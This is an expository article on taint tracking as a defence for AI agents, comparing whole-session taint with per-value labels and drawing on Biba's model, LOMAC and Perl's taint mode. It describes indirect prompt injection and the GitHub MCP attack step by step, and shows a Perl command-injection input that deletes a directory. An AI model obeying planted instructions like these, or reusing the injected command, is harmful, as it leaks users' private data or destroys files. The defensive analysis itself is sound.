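# Whole-session taint and fine-grained data labels as conditions on what an AI agent may do

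## What it means to taint an agent session or a value

An AI agent is a program in which a language model chooses actions and ordinary software carries them out. People connect agents to their mailboxes, code repositories and payment systems, and the agents also read material that strangers wrote, such as incoming mail, web pages and comments on public projects. A stranger can plant instructions in that material for the agent to follow. Model developers have made this attack harder, but nobody has made it impossible, so some security engineers leave the model as it is and limit what the agent may do after it has read something untrustworthy.

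*Taint* is a mark showing that data, or a whole context, has come under the influence of an untrusted source. With *session taint*, the software keeps one mark for everything the agent has in view, and that mark governs every later action. With *value labels*, the software marks each piece of data separately and restricts only the actions that depend on a marked piece. Both approaches are older than language models (Biba's low-water-mark rule for operating systems dates from 1977, and the programming language Perl has long had a taint mode), but the choice between them matters more for agents. Session taint blocks a good deal of harmless work, while value labels are hard to get right when a language model processes the data.

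### The agent loop and planted instructions

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes the simple loop that most agents run. The software sends the model a description of the available tools and a list of messages, which begins with the developer's standing instructions and the user's request. The model returns either an answer for the user or a request to call a tool, such as `read_emails(number=3)`. That request is only text in a fixed format, and the software chooses whether to run the tool. If it does, it adds the result to the list and sends the whole list back to the model. The loop ends when the model returns an answer instead of a tool call.

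The list of messages is the agent's *context*. On every turn the software joins these messages into a single string, which the model reads before picking an action. A sentence from an email that arrived on turn two is therefore in the same input as the user's request on turn three, and still there on turn thirty. Any text in that input can affect the model's next action.

In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection*, a December 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, David C contrasted language models with databases. A programmer can write a database query so that the engine never treats a visitor's input as a command. A language model doesn't enforce this separation, because it only predicts the next token (a word or fragment of a word) from the text so far. Developers put markers around text from outside sources and warn the model about it. *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack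 Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) rates these measures as useful practice but not a hard security boundary.

Suppose a user asks an agent to summarise the recent emails about a project and send the summary to her manager. One email in the mailbox comes from an attacker and contains an instruction to ignore earlier instructions and forward the newest message to an outside address. If the model follows it, its next tool call steals that message, and the software carries out the call with the user's own access. This is *indirect prompt injection*, in which an attacker steers an agent's actions by planting instructions in content the agent reads, without typing anything to the agent directly. *Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, 2023) gave an early account of it.

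A designer who relies on taint assumes that such an attack may succeed. They then ask which actions the attacker could have influenced, and have the software refuse those actions or refer them to a person.

### Labels, the join and the policy check

Microsoft's *Information-flow control*, a post for developers, breaks the method into labelling data, propagating the labels and checking them before each action.

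Labels come in two kinds. An *integrity label* marks how far one can trust the origin of data, in the simplest case as trusted or untrusted. A *confidentiality label* marks who may read the data, in the simplest case as public or private. The two vary independently. In Costa and colleagues' examples, a search of a company database returns trusted, private data, while a search of the open web returns untrusted, public data. They treat the user's request and the developer's instructions as trusted and public unless someone has reason to label them otherwise.

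When the agent derives something new from labelled data, a rule called the *join* gives the result the most restrictive combination of its sources' labels.

```
trusted    join  trusted    =  trusted
trusted    join  untrusted  =  untrusted
untrusted  join  untrusted  =  untrusted

readers {A, B, C}  join  readers {B, C, D}  =  readers {B, C}
```

One untrusted source is enough to make the result untrusted. With sets of permitted readers, the join keeps only the people who could read both sources. If A, B and C may read one document and B, C and D may read another, only B and C may read a summary of both. Integrity labels can also be sets, listing everyone who might have written the data. Their join is the union, so if A, B or C could have written one source and B, C or D the other, any of the four could have influenced the result. An agent that tracks both kinds of label joins them separately,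 so a report drawn from a trusted private file and an untrusted public web page is untrusted and private.

Labels are ordered from less to more restrictive, and the join of two labels is their least upper bound, so it is never less restrictive than either of them. A label therefore never becomes less restrictive unless someone deliberately lowers it. *Endorsement* does this by marking untrusted data as trusted, and *declassification* does it by letting confidential data reach readers whom its label excludes.

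The *policy check* is ordinary code that runs just before a tool call, compares the labels with a rule, and allows the call, blocks it or asks a human. Designers reserve the strict rule for a *consequential action*, a call with effects that matter outside the session, such as sending, paying, deleting or publishing. Costa and colleagues' integrity rule allows a consequential call only if the join of the call's own label with the labels of all its arguments is trusted. The call's own label is the label of the context in which the model chose it. Their confidentiality rule requires that every recipient of a message be permitted to read its contents.

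The model takes no part in the check, so planted text cannot bypass it by manipulating the model. But this guarantee depends on correct labels. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper by researchers at Google and several universities and companies, therefore counts the labels, and the code that propagates and enforces them, among the components that everyone must be able to trust.

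### The two rules on one small task

Session taint needs very little machinery.

```
context        = [developer's instructions, user's request]
context_label  = trusted

repeat:
    reply = model(context)
    if reply is an answer: show it to the user and stop
    if reply.tool is consequential and context_label is untrusted:
        block the call or ask a human
    otherwise:
        result, label = run(reply.tool, reply.arguments)
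        add result to context
        context_label = join(context_label, label)
```

*Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) applies the same idea to programming languages, using a floating "current label" that sums up all data observed so far. After a program fetches a page from phony.com, its current label includes phony.com, and an attempt to write somewhere that requires the user's own integrity raises an error. David C repeats a shorter version from an online exchange between the developers Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista. In that version, a model that processes information from some party should drop to that party's privileges.

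Value labels require the software to hold untrusted results back from the model. The version below simplifies a design by Costa and colleagues.

```
context        = [developer's instructions, user's request]
context_label  = trusted
store          = {}

repeat:
    reply = model(context)
    if reply is an answer: show it to the user and stop
    arguments = reply.arguments, with stored names replaced
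                by their values and labels
    if reply.tool is consequential and
       join(context_label, labels of arguments) is untrusted:
        block the call or ask a human
    otherwise:
        result, label = run(reply.tool, arguments)
        if label is more restrictive than context_label:
            store[new name] = (result, label)
            add only the name to context
        else:
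            add result to context
```

Now suppose the user asks the agent to fetch her three newest emails and then send her colleague Dana the message "Good morning". The emails come from outside, so the mail tool labels them untrusted.

| Step | Session taint | Value labels |
|---|---|---|
| Start | Context is trusted | Context is trusted |
| `read_emails(number=3)` | The call runs. The text of the emails joins the context, which becomes untrusted | The call runs. The software stores the emails as `emails_1`, marked untrusted, and shows the model only that name. The context stays trusted |
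| `send_message(to="Dana", text="Good morning")` | Consequential call from an untrusted context: the software blocks it or asks the user | Consequential call from a trusted context, with trusted arguments: the message goes out |

The model proposes the same calls in both columns. Under session taint, the software cannot determine whether the model proposed the greeting because the user asked for it or because an email did, so it treats the greeting as if an email had. The result also depends on the order of the requests, and session taint would have allowed both if the user had asked for the greeting before the emails.

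Value labels allow the greeting because the model chose it without the emails in its input, so an injection in them could not have influenced it. If the user had asked the agent to forward the emails to Dana, the message text would have carried the untrusted label, and the strict rule would have blocked the call. A finer policy can treat the arguments separately. Costa and colleagues would require the recipient and the decision to send to be trusted, but allow untrusted text in the message body.

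The model keeps this freedom only while it has not read the emails. The greeting doesn't require reading them, because the same calls solve the task whatever the emails contain. Costa and colleagues call such tasks data independent. They contrast these tasks with a request to complete the tasks due today in a to-do app, where the right calls depend on what is in the list. If the software puts the list into the context, the context label rises to match it, and from then on the value rule blocks consequential calls just as session taint does. Many of the things people want from an agent are more like the to-do request than the greeting.

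### How labels go wrong

The standard terms "overtainting" and "undertainting" come from the analysis of ordinary programs. *All You Ever Wanted to Know About Dynamic Taint Analysis* (Schwartz, Avgerinos and Brumley, 2010) uses overtainting for marking a value that does not derive from a tainted source, and undertainting for missing a real flow. Both errors can also occur when tracking taint in an agent's data and actions.

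*Over-tainting* means treating data or actions as untrusted although no untrusted content affected them. The blocked greeting is an example if the three emails were ordinary mail and the model did only what the user asked.

*Under-tainting* means treating data or actions as trusted even though untrusted content affected them. For example, the software might label the user's calendar trusted because it is hers, and the agent then obeys an instruction that a stranger wrote in an invitation.

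Over-tainting causes lost work or another approval request, while under-tainting can let an attack through, and reducing one often increases the other. Schwartz and colleagues give an example that long predates AI agents. The network tool tcpdump uses the first byte of each incoming packet to look up which printing routine to run. A tracker that taints any value looked up using tainted data will raise an alarm on practically every run of this harmless program. Without that rule, the tracker misses attacks that use such a lookup to choose where a program jumps next.

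*Label creep* is the tendency of labels to rise and never fall during a run, until the software blocks most actions. An agent that opens one public web page may then need a human's approval for every message it sends. *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (Gregory, Domico and colleagues, 2026) traces label creep to conservative joins in agents that keep their memory. Each exposure raises the agent's label, and nothing lowers it again without a declassification mechanism. Labels on individual values also creep, but more slowly, because a note that the agent compiles from nine trusted documents and one untrusted one is untrusted wherever it goes next. *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (2026) warns that creep can make agents unusable unless someone devises safe, automatic rules for lowering labels.

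*Implicit flow* is influence that passes through a decision rather than through copied data. If the agent sends Dana "Good morning" only when some email mentions that she is back from leave, the message contains no text from the email, but the email's author determined whether it was sent. The value rule above therefore joins the context label into its check instead of checking the arguments alone. A call such as `delete_all_drafts()` has no arguments, so a check on arguments alone would always pass it, whoever prompted it.

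Confidentiality is harder to protect against implicit flow, because an action that never happens can also leak information. Austin and Flanagan describe the problem in ordinary code in *Permissive Dynamic Information Flow Analysis*. Suppose a program sets a public variable to 1 only when a private variable has a certain value. If the program sets the public variable, the tracker can mark it private. Otherwise the program never touches it, its label stays public, and anyone who sees the old value learns something about the private variable. Similarly, an outsider watching for a message from an agent can learn something when no message arrives. The checks that Costa and colleagues propose deliberately leave this channel open. They argue that closing it would in effect require forbidding any call that writes somewhere public after any call that might have read something private.

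### Why a model makes value labels harder

Labeling values in ordinary code is mostly mechanical, because every instruction has known operands and a fixed rule determines the result's label from theirs. In an example from Schwartz and colleagues, a program reads a number from outside, doubles it, adds five, and jumps to the instruction at the resulting address. The input is tainted, so the doubled number is tainted, and so is the sum, and the tracker stops the program at the jump. A constant elsewhere in the program stays clean.

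A language model offers nothing comparable. It takes the entire context as input and produces a reply, and no instruction in between combines just the user's request with just the second email. *GIF* (2026) proposes a way to measure information flow through a model because agents break the rule-based propagation that older systems depend on. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (Wang, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) points out that an execution log can record which steps an agent took, but one has to infer whether a step depended on a particular input, for instance by removing the input and running the step again. Searching the reply for copied phrases is not enough either, since a model can act on an email without repeating a word of it.

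The safe assumption is therefore that everything the model produces depends on everything it was shown. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* states that the best anyone can currently do is give the output the union of the input labels. The paper calls the result *label explosion*, where every piece of data ends up with every label and tracking them no longer serves a purpose. If ten labelled values go into the model and one value comes out, that value carries all ten labels. At that point, value labels are no more precise than session taint and take more engineering.

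A system that labels values also has to define what counts as one value. Costa and colleagues allow a label on a whole tool result, on a single field of it, or on anything in between. That works while the data has fields, but in the context the data is a sequence of tokens, and token boundaries do not show where one source ends and the next begins. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* suggests using message boundaries instead, or the web origin of each stretch of text.

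A designer who wants finer labels than that can keep untrusted text away from the model that picks the actions, as the value rule does with `emails_1`, or give the text to a separate model call that has no tools. The remaining option is to let the model read everything and then estimate which inputs influenced it. This replaces a fixed rule with an estimate that can be wrong.

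## Biba's low-water-mark rule and Perl's taint mode

Programmers had to choose between one label for a whole program and a label for each value decades before AI agents existed. In 1977 Kenneth Biba proposed that an operating system keep a single integrity level for each running program and lower it whenever the program read something less trustworthy, which is essentially session taint. Perl's taint mode instead marks each value in a script, as value labels do. Both ideas went into working software, and both caused the kinds of problems that people who build agents should expect.

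### Three integrity rules from 1977

Biba wrote *Integrity Considerations for Secure Computer Systems* (1977) for MITRE, a research corporation that was helping the US Air Force design a secure version of the Multics operating system. Military rules already governed who could read classified information, and Biba asked who should be able to change it. One of his examples is a database of interstate transport routes that many ordinary programs read and that military logistics would depend on in an emergency. Everyone should be able to read it but almost nobody should be able to change it, and a single secrecy level can't express both requirements.

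Biba's model has *subjects*, which are programs running on behalf of a user, and *objects*, which are files and other data stores. Each has an integrity level. Biba borrowed the level names from the secrecy system (Confidential, Secret and Top Secret, in rising order), but here an object is Top Secret if its unauthorised modification could do exceptionally grave damage, even if anyone may read it. Running a file as a program counts as reading it, because the program gets its instructions from the file. A language model gets instructions from its context in much the same way.

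A hostile program can sabotage a protected file directly by overwriting it. Sabotage is indirect when a program that is allowed to write to the file reads data an attacker has tampered with and damages the file as a result. Indirect prompt injection works this way. Biba compared three rules that differ in how they treat reading. Below, `il` stands for integrity level.

```
strict integrity
    subject may read an object     only if il(subject) <= il(object)
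    subject may modify an object   only if il(object)  <= il(subject)

low-water mark
    subject may read any object;
        afterwards il(subject) = min(il(subject), il(object))
    subject may modify an object   only if il(object)  <= il(subject)

ring
    subject may read any object;   il(subject) stays the same
    subject may modify an object   only if il(object)  <= il(subject)
```

Most people now use "the Biba model" to mean strict integrity, usually summarized as "no read down, no write up". Under the low-water-mark rule, a falling integrity level is equivalent to a rising taint label in an agent, and taking the `min` of integrity levels is equivalent to taking the join of taint labels.

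Suppose a logistics program starts at Top Secret. It reads the route database, a routing subroutine from a shared library and a request file that a junior user wrote. It then tries to save a convoy schedule, which is a Top Secret object.

| Step | Strict integrity | Low-water mark | Ring |
|---|---|---|---|
| Read route database (Top Secret) | Allowed | Allowed, program stays at Top Secret | Allowed |
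| Read subroutine (Secret) | Refused | Allowed, program falls to Secret | Allowed |
| Read request file (Confidential) | Refused | Allowed, program falls to Confidential | Allowed |
| Write convoy schedule (Top Secret) | Allowed | Refused | Allowed |

The strict rule protects the schedule, but the program has to plan the convoy without its subroutine or the request. Under the low-water-mark rule, the program reads everything but can't save the result, although it could have made the same write before the second read. The ring rule lets the program do the whole job but relies on it to check its own inputs. An agent whose only defence is a model trained to ignore planted instructions works under something like the ring rule.

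Biba proved that strict integrity and the low-water-mark rule both stop indirect sabotage, meaning that no chain of reads and writes can carry information to an object at a higher level than the one it came from. Suppose program P reads file A and then writes file B. After the read, P's level is no higher than A's. P can write only to files at or below its own level, so B's level is no higher than A's. The same reasoning applies to each later read and write, so no file further down the chain has a higher level than A. The proof holds whatever a program does with the data it reads, which makes it attractive for language models, whose handling of text nobody can specify. It does depend on someone having assigned the levels correctly.

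The low-water-mark rule has what the MITRE report calls "rather disagreeable behavior". The set of files a program may modify can shrink with every read, which makes general-purpose programming awkward. A program can lose write access to files it needs to finish its work, and Biba saw no way to recover except to reinitialise the program.

Biba also considered letting the levels of objects fall. A program that had read something Confidential could still write to a Top Secret file, but the file would drop to Confidential. He rejected this for a working system because careless programs would eventually bring everything down to the lowest level, and because it would reveal improper changes without preventing them. He kept a version for auditing that doesn't restrict access but records, for each file, the least trustworthy information that could have gone into it. Whoever labels the notes an AI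 agent saves to long-term memory faces the same choice.

Biba's levels could also include *compartments*, which are named areas such as logistics or budget control. If a program cleared for logistics and budget control reads a file that belongs only to logistics, it keeps only logistics and can no longer modify budget files. Sets of permitted readers follow the same rule.

### LOMAC and self-revocation

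Tim Fraser, a researcher at NAI Labs, built the low-water-mark rule into Linux around 2000. Research projects had spent 25 years showing that mandatory access control (rules that the system imposes on every program, whatever its user wants) could work on Unix, but ordinary users had not adopted it. In *LOMAC*, Fraser (2001) attributed this to earlier systems breaking existing software, needing administration, or disrupting people's habits. He wanted a version that an administrator could load into a standard Linux kernel and then forget about.

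LOMAC has two levels. Critical system processes, system programs, libraries and configuration files are high, while network servers and clients, ordinary users' files and downloads are low. A list of 25 rules assigns levels to files by their location, and the rule with the longest matching path applies. For example, if the rules make everything high, everything inside `/home` low and `/home/httpd` high, then the web server's pages are high and a user's own documents are low.

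A file's level never changes. A process starts with the level of the process that created it, falls to low when it reads a low file, and never rises again. LOMAC also treats every network connection as a low file, so a server drops to low on receiving its first message. When an ordinary user logs in, the command shell reads that user's settings from a low directory, so everything the user starts afterward is low too. A low process can't modify high files or send signals to high processes, even if it has administrator privileges. LOMAC can't distinguish a program that has read hostile data and still works properly from one that an attacker has taken over, so it restricts both.

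The trouble that Biba had foreseen appeared in the early prototypes. In *LWM (Was RFC: Requirements...)* (2000), a message to a mailing list for FreeBSD security developers, Fraser described running the command `ps auxw | less` from a high-level shell. The program `ps` lists the running processes, `less` shows text one screen at a time, and the bar between them creates a *pipe* that carries the output of one to the other. It went wrong like this:

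1. The shell starts `ps` and `less` at high and connects them with a pipe, which is also high.
2. `ps` reads some low files that hold information about processes, and LOMAC demotes it to low.
3. `ps` tries to write its list to the pipe. A low process can't write to a high object, so LOMAC refuses.
4. `less` receives nothing and shows an empty screen.

Every step follows the rule, and no attack is involved. This is the *self-revocation* problem, in which a process loses access to something it was already using by reading. It can happen with files as well as pipes, because LOMAC compares levels at each write, not only when a program opens a file. A program could open a high file, write half of it, read one low file and then be unable to write the other half.

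Fraser dealt with this by treating all the programs that a shell starts for one command line as a single subject. When `ps` reads its low file, `ps` and `less` both fall to low. LOMAC ignores traffic on the pipe between them once it has checked that no program outside the group can use the pipe. The list appears on the screen, and the protection still holds because both programs are low. This worked for commands typed into a shell but caused problems for some scheduled background jobs, which use pipes differently. Fraser was already trying out a version in which pipes had their own levels.

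Other programs needed an exemption. The program `pump` takes network settings from a remote server and writes them into the system's configuration files, which is the kind of flow LOMAC exists to prevent. The logging program `syslogd` copies messages from low processes into a high log file. Administrators also needed `sshd` to log in remotely without being demoted. Fraser put such programs on a short list of trusted programs that LOMAC never demotes, and accepted that an attacker who took over one of them at the high level could damage the rest of the system. He also supplied a tool called `lup`, which let an administrator endorse a low file by hand, such as a downloaded update, by copying it into the high area after checking it.

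With these adjustments, LOMAC was unobtrusive, at least for one user. Fraser reinstalled it on his chief scientist's workstation and forgot to mention it, and the chief scientist didn't notice for 11 days. However, the chief scientist was using the machine only lightly, and Fraser had no formal usability study. LOMAC added a modest 3.1% to the time taken by a realistic job, building a Linux kernel, and up to about 16% in small tests of starting programs and passing data back and forth through pipes.

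The remaining gaps came from having so few labels. All temporary files were low, so editors and compilers that relied on them could not run at the high level. LOMAC did not protect one low program from another, which left users' documents exposed to a hijacked web server. An earlier version had a middle level for most users' files, but people then had to open separate text editors for files at different levels and remember which editor was at which level. Fraser left the middle level out of the later version. He told the mailing list that he had put compatibility first and quality of protection second, and that finer schemes did better at limiting each program to the privileges it needs.

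### Perl's taint mode

Perl scripts often ran on a server for strangers, such as the scripts behind early web forms. Such a script may pass a visitor's text to the operating system as part of a command. Perl's *taint mode* is meant to catch cases where the programmer forgot to check that text. Perl turns it on automatically when a script runs with the privileges of a user other than the one who started it, and a programmer can also turn it on with the `-T` switch.

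According to the Perl security manual, all data from outside the script is tainted: command-line arguments, environment variables, language and region settings, all file input and the results of certain system calls. Text that the programmer wrote in the script is clean. If an expression contains a tainted value, its result is tainted, so joining a visitor's text to the constant `bar` gives a tainted string. Each element of a list is marked separately, so a list can contain both tainted and clean values.

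Perl then refuses to use tainted data in any command that starts a shell, or that modifies files, directories or processes. The script stops with an error such as "Insecure dependency". Some of these errors are false alarms. For speed, Perl doesn't work out which part of an expression affected the result, so `$bad = ($arg, 23)` leaves `$bad` tainted by `$arg` even though its value is 23. Perl also blocks a call that only passes a tainted argument to the harmless program `/bin/echo`, because it has no information about what that program does.

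Sooner or later a script has to use what the visitor typed, so Perl needs a way to clear the mark. It does this through pattern matching. If the programmer matches a tainted string against a *regular expression*, a compact description of permitted text, the part that the pattern captures comes out clean. The interpreter doesn't judge the pattern. This script is supposed to count the lines in a report that a visitor names:

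```
#!/usr/bin/perl -T
$ENV{PATH} = '/bin:/usr/bin';
delete @ENV{'IFS', 'CDPATH', 'ENV', 'BASH_ENV'};

my $name = shift;                        # tainted
if ($name =~ /^(.+)$/) { $name = $1; }   # now clean
system "wc -l /srv/reports/$name";       # runs
```

The `ENV` lines set the list of directories the system searches for programs. Perl requires this even when a command's text is clean, because whoever controls that list can decide which program `wc` runs. The visitor's text arrives tainted in `$name`, and without the pattern on the next line, Perl would stop the script at `system`.

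Suppose the visitor supplies `march.txt; rm -r /srv/reports`. The pattern `.+` matches any run of characters, so it captures the whole string, and Perl clears the mark. The shell receives `wc -l /srv/reports/march.txt; rm -r /srv/reports`, counts the lines in the March report, and then deletes every report in the directory.

The manual's recommended pattern for such a case is `/^([-\@\w.]+)$/`, which allows only letters, digits, underscores, hyphens, at signs and dots. The visitor's string contains a semicolon, spaces and slashes, so it doesn't match, `$name` stays tainted, and Perl stops the script before the command runs. The manual advises listing the characters to allow rather than the ones to block, because it is too easy to forget a dangerous one. What counts as a letter depends on the region settings, which come from outside the script, so when a script uses those settings, text captured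 with `\w` stays tainted.

Some flows escape the tracking altogether, and the manual lists them:

- Perl doesn't check what a script prints. A script can therefore send a visitor's text straight to another program that reads its output.
- A script may open a file for reading under a tainted name, so a visitor may be able to choose which file the script reads.
- The keys of a *hash* (a table that Perl looks up by name) are never tainted. A script that counts requests by storing file names as keys gets clean names back when it lists the table, though nobody has checked them.
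- A script may use a tainted string as the name of the function or method to call. The manual warns that outsiders may then be able to reach functions the programmer never meant to expose, including one that runs arbitrary commands.
- A choice between two clean values gives a clean result, even if a tainted value made the choice. This is an implicit flow, and Perl ignores it on purpose. If a script picks one of two fixed strings according to what the visitor typed, the programmer wrote both strings.

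These omissions make sense because taint mode is meant to protect a well-meaning programmer from a hostile visitor. The mechanism is "intended to prevent stupid mistakes, not to remove the need for thought". It isn't meant to contain code written by a hostile programmer. For that, the manual points to a different tool and warns that it isn't bulletproof either.

### What became of them

The low-water-mark rule survives in FreeBSD, whose release 14.0 still included *MAC_LOMAC(4)* (2012), the manual page for its version of LOMAC. That version is more flexible than Fraser's. An administrator can let a process change its own level within a set range, and can attach a level to a program file so that a process takes on that level when it runs the program. Both features loosen the principle that a process's level can only fall. Windows Vista used a different form of integrity levels and ran Internet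 Explorer at a low level by default, so that an attacker who took over the browser would find it hard to change system files.

Perl's developers have spent more than a decade looking for ways to avoid the overhead of taint mode. It slows every Perl program to some degree, because the interpreter has to keep checking whether the feature is on. Mueller's *No-taint support in Perl* (2012) offered a way to build Perl without it and reported a "small but measurable" speed gain. *Making Taint support optional in Perl* (2021), a post that asked users for comments, gave a higher estimate of the overhead, about 10% in some scenarios, and suggested that very few people used the feature. It proposed a slow path from an optional build to possible removal. The leader of a group with dozens of web applications that relied on taint mode replied that the plan was a horrible idea.

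*Configure option for not including taint support*, a proposal that Bowers drafted and the Perl developers accepted, keeps taint support on by default but lets people build Perl without it. Thousands of published Perl packages have tests that begin with the `-T` switch, and most of them don't need it. If a Perl without taint support rejected the switch, people couldn't install much of the public library, so Bowers chose a build that accepts `-T` but ignores it. A programmer who relies on the switch therefore gets no protection and no error, a danger that Mueller had pointed out ten years earlier. In March 2023, while the developers were still deciding about the build option, Orton added settings to *Config.pm* that a script can query to find out whether its copy of Perl tracks taint.

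Ruby borrowed taint tracking from Perl, and its developers later removed it. In *Remove $SAFE, taint and trust* (2019), Naruse argued that some programmers had used it for early web scripts but that nobody did any longer. Libraries that bring in data had stopped marking it as tainted. Naruse gave the example of rack, the standard layer between Ruby programs and web servers, which returned the text of a visitor's query untainted, so a later check would have let it through as if the programmer had written it. The mechanism had also caused security holes and took a lot of work to maintain. Another developer added that even joining two strings required checking both for taint.

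No one in the discussion defended the feature as a security measure. One participant said he instead used the taint mark to track which objects his program had modified. Jeremy Evans, who did most of the work, had to coordinate changes across about 25 code repositories. Ruby 2.7 made the functions that set and clear taint do nothing.

### What the two designs predict for agents

LOMAC suggests that session taint will be sound and simple, but that people will notice it far more than Fraser's chief scientist did. LOMAC went unnoticed because its boundary was close to one Unix already had, between the administrator's files and everyone else's. Ordinary users worked at the low level all day and lost little. An agent's user typically wants to work on both sides of the boundary at once, because people often connect an agent to a mailbox so that it can read what strangers wrote and then act with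 the user's authority.

Self-revocation will therefore be common. A coding agent that starts on a fix, reads a stranger's comment on the bug and then can't submit its work is in the same position as `ps` with its pipe. Biba's solution is to restart the program, but for an agent that means starting a new session and losing whatever it had learned. Strict integrity avoids the problem by refusing the read, as GitHub Agentic Workflows now does with low-integrity content, but then the agent never sees the comment.

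There will also be pressure to exempt from session taint the agents whose purpose is to bring in outside information, as `pump` and `syslogd` do. One example is an agent that updates a project's settings from a supplier's announcements. Such an agent is hard to run under session taint, and it is also the one an attacker would most like to reach.

Ruby's experience suggests that value labels need the most care where data enters the system. Tracking is only as good as the least careful library that supplies the data, and when the default is "clean", data that a library failed to label looks the same as trustworthy data. Agents get their data from tools that many different people wrote, so a sensible system would treat unlabelled results as untrusted. Some recent work starts from the same concern, including a scheme for labelling web pages inspired by Biba. Speed should matter less than it did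 for Perl, because comparing two labels takes almost no time next to a call to a language model. Maintenance still matters, as the 25 repositories show.

Laundering looks worse for agents. A Perl programmer worries about characters that have a special meaning to the shell, and a pattern can exclude them. The careful pattern in the manual would still accept `attacker@evil.example`, because its characters are harmless. If an agent reads that address in a planted email and uses it as the recipient of a private file, a format check can confirm that it is an address but not that the user wanted to write to it. Somebody has to endorse the value for that use. The agent prototype Prudentia gives that job to the user, but a user who approves every request without reading it provides about as little protection as the pattern `.+`.

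Ignoring implicit flows, as Perl's taint mode does, won't work for agents either. It is tolerable in a script because the programmer wrote every branch beforehand, and the visitor can only choose among them. An agent's model generates each next step at run time, so a system with value labels has to check the context label as well as the arguments, and the context check follows Biba's rule.

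## Session taint against the GitHub issue attack

In May 2025 Marco Milanta and Luca Beurer-Kellner of the agent security company Invariant Labs showed that a stranger could get someone's agent to publish that person's private GitHub files. The agent had permission for every call it made, and the tools worked as intended. Applying Biba's low-water-mark rule to the agent's context stops the attack, but it also stops much of the work people connect agents to GitHub to do.

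### How the attack ran

GitHub's official MCP server gives an agent tools for reading and changing a user's *repositories*, which are project folders with a full history, and works with the user's own access key. In *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025), Invariant Labs connected the server to Anthropic's Claude Desktop application, using the model Claude 4 Opus. The test account had one public repository, containing a Pacman game, and several private ones. Anyone can open an *issue* (a bug report or a request) on a public repository.

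The researchers opened an issue on the Pacman project. Willison reproduced its text in *GitHub MCP Exploited*, a commentary with the same title. The text begins with praise for the project and regret that its author is not better known. It then gives instructions to read the README file (the introductory page) of every repository the author has, add a chapter about the author to the Pacman README, and list all the other repositories the author is working on. It also says that the author does not care about privacy. The user only had to ask the agent to look at the open issues.

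Ntousakis (2026), in *Securing MCP-based Agent Workflows*, a master's thesis at Brown University, gives the tool calls of such an attack in order:

1. `list_issues` brings the open issues of the public repository into the context, including the attacker's.
2. `list_repositories` returns every repository that the user's key can open.
3. `get_file_contents` fetches the README from each of them. One private README contains sensitive information.
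4. `create_or_update_file` writes that information into the public README as a *commit*, a recorded change that anyone can read.

In Invariant's own run, the agent instead opened a *pull request*, a proposed change that the owner may accept or refuse. The leak was just as complete, because a pull request on a public repository is visible as soon as it is opened. This one included the names of private projects, the user's salary and their plan to move to South America.

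By default, Claude Desktop asks the user to confirm individual tool calls. A user with ten repositories would have had to confirm thirteen calls during the sequence above, twelve of them reads. Milanta and Beurer-Kellner observe that many people choose "Always Allow" and stop watching. They also concluded that GitHub could not fix the problem by changing its server, since the attack can work on any agent that uses the server, whatever the model.

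### The same calls under one integrity label

Suppose the software keeps a single integrity label for the session, counts everything from a public repository as untrusted, and treats any write to GitHub as a consequential action.

| Call | Context label before the call | What the software does |
|---|---|---|
| `list_issues` | Trusted | Runs the call. The context becomes untrusted |
| `list_repositories` | Untrusted | Runs the call, which only reads |
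| `get_file_contents`, once per repository | Untrusted | Runs the calls. Private text enters the context |
| `create_or_update_file` | Untrusted | Blocks the call or asks the user |

The rule stops the attack at the last call. By then the model has read the private files, but their contents have not reached the public repository. If the software asks the user, she gets one question instead of thirteen, and she can prevent the leak by saying no.

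Session taint's success against this attack depends heavily on which actions are listed as consequential. If a designer left pull requests off the list because they only propose changes, Invariant's version of the attack would succeed. Tools that appear only to read can also leak data. Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, points out that a web request, a loaded image or a link for the user to click can each carry stolen data to an attacker. The list therefore has to include any fetch whose address the model can write.

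Now suppose the issue is an honest report from a player that the ghosts walk through walls. The user asks the agent to fix it. The agent reads the report, writes a patch and calls `create_or_update_file`, and the software stops the call as it stopped the attack. It also stops the agent from thanking the player or closing a duplicate report. If the user then dictates a line for the release notes of a private project, the software stops that too, although no stranger influenced the line. The user has to approve the write or start a new session.

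Approval is less of a burden here than in some other settings, because programmers often review a patch before merging it anyway. It works well against this attack, since a person reviewing the change will notice her own salary in it. A few lines of harmful code in a long patch would be much easier to miss.

### Why one label is enough

Session taint can stop the attack without anyone knowing why the model obeyed the issue. *Autonomous LLM Agent Worms* (2026), which concerns attacks that spread from one agent to another, defines the condition precisely. The paper uses *exposed read* for any event that loads content into the model's context, memory or configuration, or into another channel that feeds the agent. In simplified form:

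```
the session is contaminated at time t
    if there is an untrusted source s and a time r <= t
    such that an exposed read of s took place at time r
```

Like Biba's proof, the argument for safety doesn't depend on what happens to the data after the read. An attacker who works by planting text can influence an action only after an exposed read, and by then the label is untrusted.

The label stays the same if the attacker writes in another language, spreads the instruction over five issues or tells the agent to wait for twenty turns. The drawback is over-tainting, as with the line for the release notes. *Autonomous LLM Agent Worms* accepts over-tainting because no general procedure can decide whether a text materially changed a later decision.

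A finer rule must answer that question or avoid it. *Ghost in the Agent* (2026) presents NeuroTaint, a tool that tries to reconstruct the links between what an agent read and what it did. It audits offline, after the agent has acted, so it can help an investigator but can't stop a pull request.

Session taint needs no such reconstruction, so it takes little work to use. The developer can replace the model without revisiting the security argument, and the agent reads its data as usual.

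The argument holds only if the taint rule covers every route into the context and saved output keeps its label. If strangers can edit a file of standing instructions that the agent loads at startup, the session has to start as untrusted. *Autonomous LLM Agent Worms* treats everything a contaminated session produces as untrusted when an agent reads it later. Otherwise, an attacker could have the agent write an instruction into its long-term memory, and the next session would load it as the agent's own trusted work. Starting a new session, Biba's remedy for a program that has lost its privileges, would then restore those privileges with the attacker's instruction still in place.

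The paper also allows an *opaque read*, in which a trusted program reads a file without showing the model the file's contents or an open-ended description of them. For example, a program could check the digital signature on a download and return only "valid" or "invalid". This avoids some over-tainting with little effort, though the attacker still controls which answer the model gets.

### Session rules from Invariant, GitHub and Brown

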